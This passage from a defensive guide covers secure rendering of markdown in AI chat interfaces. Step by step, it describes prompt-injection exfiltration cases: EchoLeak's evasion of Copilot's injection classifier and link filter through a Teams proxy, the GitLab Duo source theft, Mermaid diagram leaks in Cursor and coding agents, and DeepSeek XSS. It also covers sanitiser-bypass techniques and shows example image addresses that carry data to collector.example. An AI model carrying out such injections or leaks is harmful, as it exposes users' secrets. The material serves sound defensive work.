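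**Python-Markdown.** Python-Markdown's *Sanitizing HTML Output* makes developers responsible for cleaning the output and recommends JustHTML, which applies a strict allowlist without further configuration. Two alternatives, nh3 and bleach, first need a suitable list of tags and attributes, and the bleach project is deprecated. According to release notes that Safety reproduces, version 3.0 of Python-Markdown ignores the library's old "safe mode" setting because the mode was never safe and gave many people false confidence.

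The PHP library league/commonmark passes raw HTML through by default, to comply with CommonMark. Developers can switch this off by setting `html_input` to `escape` or `strip`.

| Library | Raw HTML by default | How to change it |
|---|---|---|
| markdown-it | Escaped | `html: true` lets it through |
| markdown-it-py | Let through | The `js-default` preset escapes it |
| react-markdown | Escaped | `skipHtml` drops it, `rehype-raw` parses it |
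| Streamdown | Parsed and sanitised | Leaving out the parsing step escapes it |
| Marked | Let through | No simple setting, so sanitise the output |
| Python-Markdown | Let through | No simple setting, so sanitise the output |
| league/commonmark | Let through | `html_input` escapes or strips it |

Defaults differ even between versions of one library, so testing the application is more reliable than reading the documentation. A developer can have the application display a reply that contains a harmless tag, such as `<u>test</u>`, outside code formatting. If the word appears underlined, the application is rendering HTML from the reply, and the developer then needs to check whether a sanitiser runs.

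### GitHub's tag filter

The tag filter extension in GitHub's markdown dialect escapes the opening bracket of nine tags, in capitals or lower case: `title`, `textarea`, `style`, `xmp`, `iframe`, `noembed`, `noframes`, `script` and `plaintext`. It leaves all other tags unchanged, so it only partly switches off raw HTML.

According to GitHub, these nine tags are on the list because each changes how the browser interprets the HTML that follows it, as the stray `<title>` did when it swallowed the rest of an answer. The filter works well for its main purpose, which is to keep one careless tag from spoiling the surrounding page. But in the hostile reply, the handler is on a `<div>`, which is not on the list, and the filter doesn't check attributes, so it would copy the element into the page with its code intact.

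GitHub relies on its sanitiser for security, so an application that copies only the tag filter lacks that protection. Micromark's developers, whose parser is used in react-markdown, supply the filter as an add-on for matching GitHub's behaviour and describe it as "a naïve attempt at XSS protection". Marked doesn't implement the filter. In its published conformance results, Marked passes all 44 tests for HTML blocks and all 20 for inline HTML, but fails the only test for the tag filter. A high score on such tests shows that a converter follows the specification, which here includes copying hostile tags into the output unchanged.

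### What remains once raw HTML is off

**Script addresses.** A link can run code without any raw HTML. If its address starts with `javascript:`, the browser runs the rest of the address as a program in the page when the user clicks. Such an address can appear in an ordinary markdown link or in an autolink, which is an address between angle brackets that the parser turns into a link. For autolinks, MacFarlane's CommonMark Spec accepts as a scheme (the part before the colon) almost any string of 2 to 32 characters that starts with a letter, including invented ones.

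Some libraries restrict link addresses themselves. markdown-it blocks `javascript:`, `vbscript:` and `file:` addresses. It also blocks `data:` addresses, which contain a file's content instead of its location, except for four common image formats. react-markdown is stricter and permits only six schemes (`http`, `https`, `irc`, `ircs`, `mailto` and `xmpp`) plus addresses relative to the current page. A developer can replace that check with a custom `urlTransform` function, but a careless replacement can let dangerous addresses through. Marked and Python-Markdown have no such check, so an application that only escapes HTML before passing text to them still needs to check link addresses.

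Remote images also survive, since an `https` address passes every scheme check above.

Plugins are harder to handle safely because they can produce HTML after the converter has escaped everything. A syntax highlighter, for example, colours code samples by wrapping words in tags, so the converter has to trust the HTML it returns. In markdown-it, if a highlighter returns an empty string, the library escapes the code itself, but it inserts any other result unchanged. A homemade highlighter that returns unfamiliar code as it is will therefore turn a harmless sample into live HTML. TanStack explains that its own markdown renderer cannot distinguish a highlighter's tags from injected ones in the returned string.

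Some add-ons create HTML attributes from markdown text. Tomalty's 2012 bug report for the web framework Django, *Markdown filter "safe" mode is vulnerable to e.g. 'onclick' attributes*, showed that a short expression in curly brackets could attach an event handler to a paragraph. Python-Markdown's safe mode did not remove the expression because it contained no HTML tag.

Even an attribute without code can do damage. A plugin may give each heading an `id` based on its wording, so that other pages can link to it. Browsers make elements available to scripts under their `id` or `name`, so a heading with the right wording can take the place of a value that the page's own code expects, which is known as DOM clobbering. markdown-it advises plugin writers to put a fixed prefix before any `id` or `name` that depends on users' text. More generally, unified recommends running a sanitiser after all the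 plugins, so that it also checks what they add.

### Script injection in chat interfaces

Rehberger published the best-known case in November 2024, in *DeepSeek AI: From Prompt Injection To Account Takeover*. He asked DeepSeek's chat website to print a list of XSS examples, and the page ran one instead of displaying it. He then showed that planted text could make the page run code in another user's browser. The text contained HTML encoded in Base64, which the model decoded and wrote into its reply. The code could read the user's login token from the browser's storage, and anyone with that token could use the account. DeepSeek fixed the flaw before he published. His first request was an ordinary one about HTML, and escaping the HTML in the model's replies would have displayed the examples correctly and prevented the attack.

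Open WebUI, a chat interface that organisations run on their own servers, had a comparable flaw until version 0.6.6. The public advisory CVE-2025-46719 (2025) traces it to the way the interface rendered certain HTML tags in chat messages, which let an attacker inject code that ran every time someone opened the conversation. Users could share conversations, so one malicious conversation could reach many people. The code could steal the reader's access token. If the reader was an administrator, the attacker could then run programs on the server, because Open WebUI lets administrators add Python functions.

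In LobeChat, another open-source chat interface, the flaw was in an added feature that recognised a special tag in replies for "artifacts", pieces of content displayed in their own panel. When the artifact was an SVG drawing, a format that can contain scripts, LobeChat inserted it into the page through React's equivalent of `innerHTML`. According to the advisory CVE-2025-59417 (2025), anyone who could influence a chat message could exploit this, for instance with a web page containing a prompt injection. Version 1.129.4 fixed the flaw. Escaping ordinary HTML would not have helped, because the feature was meant to turn that part of the reply back into live content. An application that only needs to show a drawing can load the SVG through an image element, where browsers do not run its scripts.

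Open WebUI needed another fix in November 2025, this time in the box where users type. Users could save prompts for colleagues to insert with a short command, and when a rich-text setting was on, the interface assigned the saved prompt to `innerHTML` without sanitising it. The earlier fix had covered chat messages, but saved prompts entered the page by a different route. CVE-2025-64495 (2025) lists 0.6.35 as the first safe version.

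## Choosing which markdown features to allow

Turning off raw HTML removes one node type from the syntax tree, but the application still has to decide which of the others to render. The safest way is to use an allowlist, so that the application renders only the node types its developers have chosen and shows everything else as text. Any feature that a parser upgrade or plugin adds then stays plain text until a developer allows it, whereas developers would have to extend a blocklist to refuse it.

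When an application displays a refused element as text, what it prints depends on the element's type. It can print the link text for a link and the alternative text for an image. For anything else, it can print the original characters, since most parsers record where each node starts and ends in the source.

Markdown libraries restrict features in different ways. react-markdown has an `allowedElements` option, which takes a list of HTML element names. The library removes any element not on the list, along with its contents, unless the developer also sets `unwrapDisallowed`, which keeps the text inside. In markdown-it, a developer can switch off a parser rule, which can have unexpected results. For example, with the image rule off, `![chart](/sales.png)` becomes an exclamation mark followed by a working link.

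### Filtering the tree instead of the text

A pattern that searches the raw text has to match every way of writing a feature, and markdown has several for a link alone:

```
inline       [the report](https://collector.example/?d=4731)

reference    [the report][r]

             [r]: https://collector.example/?d=4731

in the tree, for both
  link       wording "the report"
             address https://collector.example/?d=4731
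```

An address can also contain character references. CommonMark turns `&#58;` into a colon, so a pattern for `https://` doesn't match `https&#58;//collector.example`, but the link still works. A filter on the parsed tree checks the decoded address.

Markdown converters can parse the same reply differently, so a check on the server can miss something that the browser renders with another library. The filter should therefore run in the renderer, on the tree being rendered, after any plugin that adds to that tree. TanStack checks addresses in the parser, so the check covers reference-style links and images as well as inline ones.

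### EchoLeak

Microsoft 365 Copilot, which can read an employee's mail and files, had a link filter that recognised only one of the two forms above. Aim Labs, the research team at Aim Security, used this in an attack called EchoLeak and reported the flaw (CVE-2025-32711) to Microsoft in January 2025. Ravia (2025), in *Breaking down 'EchoLeak', the First Zero-Click AI Vulnerability*, calls the technique an "LLM Scope Violation" because text from outside an organisation made the model use data from inside it. Reddy and Gujral (2025), in *EchoLeak*, reconstruct the attack step by step from published material, but they did not reproduce it and had no access to Microsoft's filters.

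The attacker sends an employee an ordinary-looking email that contains instructions for the model. When the employee later asks Copilot a question about work, Copilot's search retrieves the email alongside internal documents. The model then follows the instructions and puts the most sensitive details it can find into a URL.

The email first had to get past Microsoft's XPIA (cross-prompt injection attempt) classifier. An order to ignore previous instructions would have triggered it, so Aim Labs worded the email as a request to its human reader. Aim Labs also included an instruction, supposedly for compliance, not to mention the email in the answer, so that the employee would not learn where the odd content came from.

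The model then had to include a link in its answer. Microsoft's output filter removed links of the form `[text](address)` before the user saw them. It missed reference-style links, so the link reached the user with the internal data in its address. At this stage the employee still had to click it.

To avoid needing a click, the researchers had the model write a reference-style image, which also passed the filter. The browser then requested the image's address automatically, but the request failed because Copilot's content security policy allowed images only from listed hosts, and the attacker's server was not one of them.

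One listed host belonged to Microsoft Teams, which fetches outside images through a proxy to show previews of links that people post. SC Media quotes a forum comment in which a Microsoft employee had explained this. The proxy accepted the outside address as a parameter, so the model wrote an image address on the Teams host that contained the attacker's address and the stolen data. The browser contacted Teams, Teams contacted the attacker's server, and that server logged the data. The victim saw at most what looked like a broken image.

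Microsoft had begun repairs by April, completed a fix on its own servers in May, and published its advisory on 11 June 2025. Customers had nothing to install, and Microsoft said it had no evidence that anyone had used the attack. According to Reddy and Gujral, Copilot now strips reference-style links and embedded images from outside content before the model reads it. This removes ready-made links, but an attacker can still plant text that describes an address in words, which the model can then assemble into a link, so an application still needs to check the output.

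Reddy and Gujral call EchoLeak the first known prompt injection to steal data from a production system, but this is doubtful because Rehberger reported leaks through images in 2023. EchoLeak is a useful case because it got past so many barriers. A filter on the syntax tree would have caught the reference-style link and the first version of the image, but would have missed the last version if the filter allowed all of Microsoft's hosts.

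In their table of defences, Reddy and Gujral expect an allowlist of markdown features to fail against the automatic image request. They reached this conclusion by reasoning and did not test it, and it depends on which features the list allows. The safe subset they recommend elsewhere in the paper includes plain images. A subset without remote images would have stopped the request before the browser applied the content security policy.

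### What each feature can do

Emphasis, headings, lists, quotations, tables and code formatting cannot start a request or run a program, though the text in them can be false. Links and images can start requests. Mathematics, diagrams and embedded graphics each need an interpreter for their own language, and that language may have its own links and images.

| Feature | What it can cause | Safe setting |
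|---|---|---|
| Emphasis, lists, tables, code | Nothing beyond the text | Allow |
| Links | A request on a click | Allow a few schemes, after parsing the address |
| Images | An automatic request | Allow only the application's own image server, or none |
| Mathematics in KaTeX | Links, images and HTML attributes if trusted, and a frozen page | Leave `trust` off and limit sizes |
| Diagrams in Mermaid | Images, links and changes to the page's style | Show the source as code, or use the `sandbox` level and block outside requests |
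| Embedded SVG graphics | Scripts and outside files | Show the source as code, or load the drawing through an image element |

An allowlist that permits code blocks has to check their labels too, because many chat interfaces pass a block labelled `mermaid` to a diagram library. The syntax tree represents this block as an ordinary code node, so checking the node type alone won't identify it.

Images with the scheme `data:` hold their content in the address, so the browser makes no request to load them. This means they can't be used as tracking pixels, although Streamdown's documentation gives tracking pixels as a reason to turn them off. They can still deceive readers, for example by showing a QR code.

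### Checking an address

For links, `https` is enough for most applications, perhaps with `http` and `mailto`. Listing permitted schemes is safer than listing forbidden ones. KaTeX, a popular library for displaying formulas, lets developers supply a function that accepts or refuses each address. GitLab's *Advisories for Npm/Katex package* includes a 2024 entry in which a scheme written in capitals got past a function that refused only `javascript`. A function that accepted only `https` would have refused it. KaTeX now converts the scheme to lower case before the function checks it.

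Some schemes, such as `vscode:` for a code editor or `slack:` for a chat program, open another program on the user's computer. That program receives text that an attacker may have written, so safety depends on how carefully it handles that text. The documentation of the filtering tool rehype-harden, reproduced in Pkg Stats' *rehype-harden*, describes custom schemes as safe because nothing runs in the browser, but this reasoning covers only the page. A chat application should allow such a scheme only when it has a use for it.

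For images, the host matters as well. A common mistake is to check whether the address starts with a trusted string such as `https://example.com`:

| Address | Starts with the trusted string | Host the browser contacts |
|---|---|---|
| `https://example.com/a.png` | Yes | `example.com` |
| `https://example.com.collector.example/a.png` | Yes | `example.com.collector.example` |
| `https://example.com@collector.example/a.png` | Yes | `collector.example` |
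| `HTTPS://EXAMPLE.COM/a.png` | No | `example.com` |
| `//collector.example/a.png` | No | `collector.example` |

Whoever owns a domain can create host names under it, so the owner of `collector.example` can create the host in the second row. In the third row, everything before the `@` is a user name. The address in the last row begins with two slashes. A check that allows relative addresses may accept it because addresses within the application's own site also begin with a slash, but the browser treats what follows the two slashes as a host name.

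Anthropic's coding agent Claude Code had this flaw before version 1.0.111. It could fetch pages from a few trusted domains without asking the user, and it checked for them with JavaScript's `startsWith()` function. NVD's *CVE-2026-24052 Detail* explains that an attacker could register a domain such as `modelcontextprotocol.io.example.com`, which begins with the name of a trusted site. Claude Code would then have sent requests to the attacker automatically. GitLab's *CVE-2026-24052* (2026) lists the flaw under 3 February 2026.

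The remedy is to parse the address before comparing anything, with the same rules the browser will use. In JavaScript the built-in `URL` class does this:

```js
const ALLOWED = new Set(["https://images.assistant.example"]);

function checkImage(address) {
  let url;
  try {
    url = new URL(address, "https://assistant.example");
  } catch {
    return null;
  }
  return ALLOWED.has(url.origin) ? url.href : null;
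}
```

The `URL` class converts the scheme and host to lower case, removes tabs and line breaks, and resolves relative addresses against the application's own address. Comparing origins exactly checks the scheme, host and port together. The function returns the parsed address, which the application should write into the page in place of the original string so that the browser uses the same text that passed the check. Most applications allow links to any site, so for links they would compare `url.protocol` with the permitted schemes instead of comparing origins.

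Allowing subdomains can let unsafe hosts through. A check that the host ends in `example.com` accepts `badexample.com` unless the comparison includes the dot before the name. Even with the dot, the check accepts every service under that domain, including any that relays requests to other hosts. For example, an entry for all of `microsoft.com` would have allowed the Teams proxy that EchoLeak used.

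Limiting the rule to a folder, such as `https://example.com/images/`, blocks redirect services elsewhere on the same host. The check has to use the parsed path, because `/images/../redirect` starts with the right folder but resolves to `/redirect`. Some servers also decode `%2F` into a slash after the browser has sent the request, which no check in the page can fully account for.

### Two tools that apply such rules

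rehype-sanitize and rehype-harden are plugins for the family of tools that react-markdown belongs to, and both work on a syntax tree of the HTML. unified's *rehype-sanitize* removes every element and attribute that its schema does not list, with a default schema modelled on GitHub's. In the documentation's example it deletes a script, an embedded frame and several event handlers. It also takes the address off a link whose `javascript:` scheme is disguised with mixed capitals and a space.

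In the same example, rehype-sanitize keeps the image but removes its handler. By default it does not limit which hosts images may come from, so an application that runs it alone would still leak the door code from the mailbox. It also prefixes every `id` and `name` with `user-content-` to prevent DOM clobbering. This breaks links to headings within the reply, which GitHub repairs with a small script that looks for the prefixed name.

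rehype-harden supplies the address rules. Without any settings it blocks all links and images. The developer then lists permitted prefixes, and the tool requires an address to match both the prefix and the origin. The origin check makes an entry without a final slash, such as `https://github.com`, safe in this tool. Copied into a program that uses only `startsWith()`, the same entry would recreate the Claude Code flaw.

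The documentation contradicts itself about paths. According to one passage, the tool does not resolve `/../` and leaves this to the web server, but according to the feature list, it does. A developer who relies on folders should test how the tool handles `/../`.

A blocked link normally appears as its text followed by "[blocked]", and a blocked image appears as a note with its alternative text. The developer can instead show only the text or remove the item. The visible note is more useful in a chat, because an unexpected blocked image is one of the few signs of prompt injection that a user sees.

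Streamdown includes both plugins, but its default settings for rehype-harden allow all images and links. These defaults don't stop image leaks, though a team could assume they do because the renderer has a hardening step. Streamdown's documentation gives a stricter configuration for model output. It also warns that passing in a custom list of plugins replaces the whole standard list, so leaving out the sanitiser removes the protection against XSS.

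The same documentation shows how to route every image through the application's own content server, with the original address as a parameter. Unless that server checks where each request is going, it is the same kind of relay as the Teams proxy, on a host that the application's own rules permit.

### Mathematics

Models write formulas in LaTeX, a typesetting language, and KaTeX turns them into HTML. In KaTeX, `\href` and `\url` create links, `\includegraphics` loads an image, and four commands beginning with `\html` set attributes on the page's elements. A filter on the markdown tree misses these links and images because the tree contains only a mathematics node for the formula.

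KaTeX's *Options* puts all of these commands under one setting, `trust`, which is off by default. When it is off, KaTeX only prints the command in the error colour. Keeping it off also avoids two published flaws. According to an advisory on GitHub, KaTeX versions before 0.16.10 did not properly quote the file name in `\includegraphics`, so a crafted name could run a script. Tenable's *CVE-2025-23207* describes a similar flaw in `\htmlData`, which was fixed in version 0.16.21.

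Developers who want links in formulas can set `trust` to a function, and the documentation offers samples. One allows every command and forbids only the `file` scheme, so `javascript` links would still work. A better sample allows only `\url` and `\href`, and only with a listed scheme.

unified's documentation recommends running rehype-sanitize before KaTeX, with an exception for the two class names that mark a formula. If the sanitiser runs afterwards, it strips the classes and styles that KaTeX needs, and a formula consisting of the letter L comes out as three plain Ls. Sanitising first means that KaTeX's output goes into the page unsanitised, so KaTeX's own settings have to be right. An application can still run rehype-harden last to check any links and images that KaTeX has produced.

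A formula can also disrupt the page without running code. KaTeX sets no limit on sizes by default, so a formula could cover the window with a black rectangle. Setting `maxSize` to a few dozen ems (one em is the current font size) prevents that. `maxExpand`, which defaults to 1,000 expansions, stops formulas that define endlessly looping commands. GitLab lists two vulnerabilities from 2024 that bypass this limit and could freeze the reader's browser tab, so using a patched version of KaTeX is as important as the setting.

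If a chat application passes the same `macros` object to KaTeX each time, a formula can redefine a command for all later formulas. A hostile reply could then make a later one show a plus sign where the model wrote a minus. Creating a new object for each message prevents this. According to KaTeX's documentation, its error messages may also contain the formula's source unescaped, so an application that inserts them into the page as HTML lets raw HTML back in through a broken formula.

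### Diagrams

Mermaid is a JavaScript library that draws flowcharts and other diagrams from short text descriptions. Models can write these descriptions easily, so many assistants render the diagrams automatically. The diagrams can include images, but Mermaid usually runs in the browser after the markdown tree is finished, so plugins such as rehype-harden don't check those images.

Lee, Kim and colleagues (2025) found this route while examining eight coding agents for *Takedown*. Coding agents are assistants that edit files and run commands on a programmer's computer. The researchers recorded the messages between each agent and its model, and studied the agents' code where they could. They found 15 security issues and combined them into complete attacks. Without the user's approval, they could run any command in five agents and steal files from anywhere on the machine in four.

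One theft used a diagram to send out a secret key. A programmer asks an agent, which Lee and colleagues call A2, to retrieve the issues reported for a project. One issue contains planted instructions to read a settings file where programmers often keep secret keys. A2 reads the file without asking, even though the file is outside the project. The model then writes a diagram with an image in one of its boxes and puts the key in the image's address. When the agent draws the diagram, loading the image sends the key out. Approval prompts for commands or web tools do not cover this route, because drawing a reply does not count as using a tool. The vendor marked the report of this flaw as a duplicate.

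Rehberger found the same weakness in Cursor, a code editor with a built-in assistant, and reported it on 30 June 2025. Embrace The Red's *Cursor IDE* describes how he hid the instructions in a comment in a small C program and asked Cursor to explain the file. One version of the attack sent out keys from a configuration file, and another sent out what Cursor had remembered about the user. Rehberger notes that the diagram appears already finished, so the user has no chance to notice a long address while Cursor writes the reply.

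Cursor fixed the flaw in version 1.3, according to MITRE's August record, *Cursor's Mermaid Diagram Tool is Vulnerable to an Arbitrary Image Fetch* (2025). MITRE published a second record, *Cursor* (2025), two months later because people had found ways around the fix. Version 1.7 closed them. Like links in markdown, loading something in a diagram language can be written in more than one way.

Mermaid's *Usage* describes four values for the `securityLevel` setting. The default, `strict`, encodes HTML tags in the diagram's text and disables clicks. `loose` allows HTML tags and clicks. `antiscript` does too, but removes script elements only, so an image tag would remain. `sandbox` draws the diagram in a sandboxed frame where no JavaScript runs. Lee and colleagues point to Mermaid's image shape, where the picture is specified in the diagram's own syntax. Encoding HTML tags may not block such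 an image, so `strict` alone is weak protection against leaks.

Three advisories from May 2026 show further limits of `strict`. OSV's *Mermaid* (2026), an entry in an open database of software flaws, describes a style definition in a state diagram that could add HTML to the page outside the drawing. Mermaid removed script tags, but the demonstration still covered the whole window with a panel chosen by the attacker, which could just as easily have been a fake login form.

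In a related flaw, also recorded by OSV, Mermaid's parser accepted everything up to the end of the line as a style. A closing bracket ended the intended style rule, and whatever followed became a new rule for the entire page. Style rules can load images conditionally, for example only if the page contains an element with a certain attribute value. An attacker could learn such values from which images the browser requested, without running a script or having the model read them. A third flaw let a diagram inject styles through configuration in its own text, and OSV suggests adding those options to Mermaid's `secure` list, which diagrams cannot change. Versions 11.15.0 and 10.9.6 fix all three flaws.

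The `sandbox` level also prevents all three from affecting the page. It does not by itself prevent leaks through images, because a browser loads images inside a sandboxed frame unless another rule forbids it.

Links in diagrams need the same care as other links. In October 2025, Red Hot Cyber's *A serious bug in Microsoft 365 Copilot leads to data exfiltration* reported an attack by the researcher Adam Logue. Instructions planted in an Office document made Copilot collect the user's recent emails and draw a Mermaid diagram that looked like a login button, whose link contained the encoded emails. Clicking it sent the emails to Logue's server and showed the user an imitation of Microsoft's login page, as CyberMaterial describes. Microsoft responded by disabling links in the Mermaid diagrams that Copilot generates.

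An application that must show diagrams can avoid most of this by rendering them in a separate process with no network access and serving the result from its own server as a flat image. The process cannot fetch outside images, and the flat image contains no links or styles. Users can no longer click on parts of the diagram or select its text. If diagrams are rare, the application can show the Mermaid source as a code block, which requires no extra work and which a programmer can usually read.

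## Sanitisers: how HTML is cleaned and how cleaning fails

An application needs a sanitiser if it has to show real HTML from a reply, or if it uses a converter that lets raw HTML through, such as Marked or Python-Markdown.

Klein and Johns, in *Parse Me, Baby, One More Time* (2024), describe the usual method. The sanitiser parses the HTML into a tree, ideally the same one a browser would build. It then checks each element and attribute in the tree against an allowlist and removes any that are not listed. Finally, it serialises the cleaned tree, writing it out as a new string of HTML. Some sanitisers can return the tree itself instead.

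DOMPurify, made by the security company Cure53, does this inside the browser with the browser's own parser. With its default settings, it has this effect on the hostile reply from the mailbox:

```
after markdown conversion                   after DOMPurify

<p>Here is a summary of the message.</p>    unchanged
<table>three delivery dates</table>         unchanged
<div onclick="...">Parcel details</div>     <div>Parcel details</div>
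<img src="https://collector.example/        unchanged
     p.png?d=4731">
<a href="https://collector.example/">       unchanged
     bank.example</a>
```

The sanitiser removes the handler, but the browser still requests the image, and that request sends the door code out of the mailbox. Cure53 built DOMPurify to prevent XSS, not exfiltration. In the first sample in Cure53's *DOMPurify* documentation, the image also loses its handler but keeps its address.

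### What the default settings let through

GitLab, a code-hosting platform, had this gap in Duo, its assistant based on Anthropic's Claude. Legit Security's *Remote Prompt Injection in GitLab Duo Leads to Source Code Theft* (May 2025) explains the attack. Duo followed instructions hidden in source code, commit messages, and the descriptions of proposed changes and comments on them. It began displaying its replies before they were complete, and it rendered the HTML in them after passing it through DOMPurify. This stopped the researchers from running code but left `img`, `form` and `a` elements in place.

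The researchers hid instructions in a proposed change to a public project. When the victim asked Duo an ordinary question about the file, Duo read code from a private project the victim could access, encoded it in Base64 and added it to an image's address. The victim's browser requested the image, and the researchers decoded the private code from the request. The same method could have exposed confidential reports of unfixed security flaws.

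Legit Security reported the problem on 12 February 2025. GitLab changed Duo so that it no longer renders elements such as `img` and `form` if they point outside gitlab.com. Like any host allowlist, this fails if a permitted host relays requests elsewhere.

DOMPurify also permits forms and styles by default. A form in a reply can put a password box inside the assistant's own page and send whatever the user types to an outside server. A style element can hide a warning or cover the page, and it can load images, as the Mermaid flaws showed.

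A developer could forbid `img`, `form` and `style` by name with the `FORBID_TAGS` setting, but the browser would still load the preview picture of a video or a background image in a `style` attribute. It is safer to list the few elements that markdown produces:

```js
const SETTINGS = {
  ALLOWED_TAGS: ["p", "br", "hr", "h1", "h2", "h3", "h4", "strong",
    "em", "del", "code", "pre", "blockquote", "ul", "ol", "li",
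    "table", "thead", "tbody", "tr", "th", "td", "a"],
  ALLOWED_ATTR: ["href"],
  ALLOW_DATA_ATTR: false,
  ALLOW_ARIA_ATTR: false,
  ALLOWED_URI_REGEXP: /^(?:https?|mailto):/i,
};

const clean = DOMPurify.sanitize(html, SETTINGS);
```

The last setting restricts links to three schemes, whereas the default permits eleven, including `sms` and `tel`, as well as relative addresses. These settings remove the image from the hostile reply and reduce the `<div>` to its text. The false bank link survives because it uses a normal `https` address. Harmless replies also suffer slightly, as code samples lose the class names that some highlighters need, and a numbered list that should start at 4 starts at 1.

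If the application has its own image server, the developer can add `img` to the permitted elements and `src` and `alt` to the permitted attributes, and then check each address with the `checkImage` function shown earlier. DOMPurify runs such checks through hooks, functions that it calls at set points in the walk:

```js
DOMPurify.addHook("afterSanitizeAttributes", (node) => {
  if (node.tagName !== "IMG") return;
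  const address = checkImage(node.getAttribute("src") ?? "");
  if (address) node.setAttribute("src", address);
  else node.removeAttribute("src");
});
```

Developers should not combine `ALLOWED_TAGS` with `USE_PROFILES`, a shortcut for permitting all safe HTML, because `USE_PROFILES` overrides the list and allows images and forms again.

### Sanitise after conversion and change nothing afterwards

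A sanitiser has to run on the HTML that the markdown converter produces. A markdown link to a `javascript:` address contains no HTML tag, so a sanitiser run on the markdown would miss it, and the converter would then make it a live link. Sanitising the markdown also damages harmless replies. The sanitiser does not recognise code fences, so it strips tags from code samples, and it turns the `>` at the start of a markdown quotation into `&gt;`.

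Sanitising should also be the last change before display. Cure53 warns that editing the HTML afterwards can easily undo the cleaning. Sonar's *mXSS Explained* calls this mistake "desanitization" and reports finding it in several applications.

An application may sanitise a reply and then use text replacement to turn every bare web address into a link. If an address is inside an attribute, such as a link's tooltip, the replacement inserts quotation marks there. The first one ends the attribute early, and the browser parses the address as further attributes. An attacker who chose the address can make one of these an event handler. The application can avoid this by creating the links in the markdown tree, before sanitising. Formulas are the exception to this order because KaTeX has to run after the sanitiser.

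### HTML that changes when the browser parses it again

Sanitising can fail even if the application doesn't change the cleaned string afterwards, because the browser parses it again. Browsers repair faulty HTML instead of rejecting it, and a repair can move elements. In a harmless example from aszx87410's *Mutation XSS*, a page puts a heading inside a table, where headings are not allowed, and the browser moves it in front of the table.

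A tree can change when a program serialises it and parses the result. The security company Securitum gives the example of `<svg></p>`, a drawing that contains a stray closing tag. An affected browser parsed this as a drawing with an empty paragraph inside and serialised it as `<svg><p></p></svg>`. When the browser parsed that string, it moved the paragraph out of the drawing, because an opening `<p>` tag ends a drawing. Everything after the paragraph moved out too, and HTML has different parsing rules outside a drawing.

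In mutation XSS, an attacker gets code past a sanitiser by exploiting changes the browser makes to HTML when it parses it. The first known case dates from 2007, when the researcher Hasegawa found that one browser mishandled the backtick character. *mXSS attacks* (2013), by Heiderich, Schwenk and colleagues, showed that this bug belonged to a whole class affecting Internet Explorer, Firefox and Chrome. The team stored working attacks in Yahoo! Mail, Roundcube and other webmail products. Browser makers fixed the bugs behind these early attacks, and later attacks rely instead on differences between the sanitiser's parser and the browser's.

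Klein and Johns work through an example with a sanitiser that permits formulas (`math`) and embedded frames (`iframe`) and removes every image. The attacker puts an image with a handler inside a frame inside a formula:

```
the sanitiser's tree              the browser's tree

math                              math
  iframe                            iframe
    text "<img ...>"              img, with its handler
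```

In ordinary HTML, everything inside an `iframe` element counts as text. The sanitiser applies that rule, so it stores the image tag as text, finds no image to remove, and writes the text back unchanged. The browser then parses the result by the rules for formulas, where `iframe` has no special meaning and its contents are markup. When the browser reaches the image tag, which can't be part of a formula, it closes the formula and adds the image to the page after it. The image fails to load, which triggers the handler.

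The text editor Jodit had a flaw of this kind. According to XDSoft's *Mutation XSS via MathML*, the attack hid an image tag as text in a style element, inside a table and a formula. Jodit's sanitiser checked only elements, so it missed the tag, which the second parse turned into an element.

An application can avoid the second parse by using the cleaned tree instead of a string. DOMPurify returns the tree if the developer sets `RETURN_DOM_FRAGMENT`, and the application can attach it directly to the page. react-markdown also builds page elements from its cleaned tree. A server can't avoid the second parse, because it can only send text to the browser.

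### A test of eleven sanitisers

To find out how often servers get this wrong, Klein and Johns wrote a program called MutaGen, which takes a simple piece of HTML that runs code and wraps it in up to 25 layers of hard-to-parse markup. They generated 12 million different fragments and ran them through 11 sanitisers for JavaScript, .NET, PHP, Ruby and Java. Then they loaded the results in Chromium, Firefox and WebKit (Safari's engine) and recorded whether the code ran. They tested most sanitisers twice, once with the default settings and once with lenient settings that allowed every tag MutaGen used.

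They got code past nine of the 11 sanitisers, including six with default settings. The table shows some of the results. The last column compares the sanitiser's tree with Chromium's, and a score of 1 means the two were identical.

| Sanitiser | Fragments that ran code, default settings | Lenient settings | Match with Chromium |
|---|---|---|---|
| rgrove/sanitize (Ruby) | 0 | 2,178 | 0.94 |
| HtmlSanitizer (.NET) | 0 | 966 | 0.90 |
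| DOMPurify with jsdom 22 | 0 | 341 | 0.87 |
| DOMPurify with jsdom 19 | 31 | 154 | 0.88 |
| TYPO3 html-sanitizer (PHP) | 4,754 | 52,214 | 0.52 |
| sanitize-html (JavaScript) | 0 | 0 | 0.39 |
| loofah (Ruby) | 0 | Not adjustable | 0.22 |

The counts are a poor measure of how serious each flaw was, since thousands of fragments can exploit the same flaw. Klein and Johns traced the results to 16 flaws, not counting those in two abandoned libraries. Most of the bypasses that needed the extremely lenient settings would also have worked if a developer had allowed just one or two extra tags.

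The two sanitisers that nothing got past, sanitize-html and loofah, were among the worst at parsing HTML the way the browser does. They were safe because they escape text when they write out the result, so an image tag that the sanitiser's parser has mistaken for text stays text in the browser. Klein and Johns estimate that this escaping alone would have prevented 14 of the 16 flaws. The drawback is that both libraries mangle more markup that is harmless.

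In 19,843 cases, sanitising made a harmless fragment dangerous. DOMPurify had a flaw like this when it ran on a server with version 19 of jsdom, a library that imitates a browser's DOM. Sanitising turned a properly escaped image tag into a live one.

Browsers also handle some HTML differently. Firefox departed from the HTML standard in how it handled some drawings, so a fragment that was safe in Chromium ran code in Firefox. A server that cleans HTML once for everyone can't account for these differences. Klein and Johns conclude that no sanitiser on a server can be both accurate and secure. Sonar's *Sanitize Client-Side* traces a series of bypasses in most PHP sanitisers to the parser they used, and also argues for cleaning HTML in the browser.

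A strict sanitiser on the server can work well for a chat application, because headings, lists and tables from a markdown converter are simple HTML and losing an unusual drawing does little harm. But the test can't prove that sanitize-html and loofah are safe. For example, MutaGen did not generate any CSS, which had recently been the source of a flaw in rgrove/sanitize.

### DOMPurify's advisories and the need to update

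DOMPurify did well in the test, but researchers keep finding ways to bypass it. In October 2026, Snyk listed 44 vulnerabilities in the library, none of which affected version 3.4.17, the latest at the time.

Several fixes needed follow-ups. In 2024 a researcher got past DOMPurify with very deeply nested elements, which browsers rearrange. Cure53 then limited nesting to 255 levels. Tenable's *CVE-2024-47875* (2024) rates the nesting flaw 10, the maximum severity on one scoring system, and lists 3.1.3 as the first safe version in the main series. Cure53's *Releases* told users to upgrade immediately and warned that variations might follow. They soon did, and another researcher then found a way around the depth check itself.

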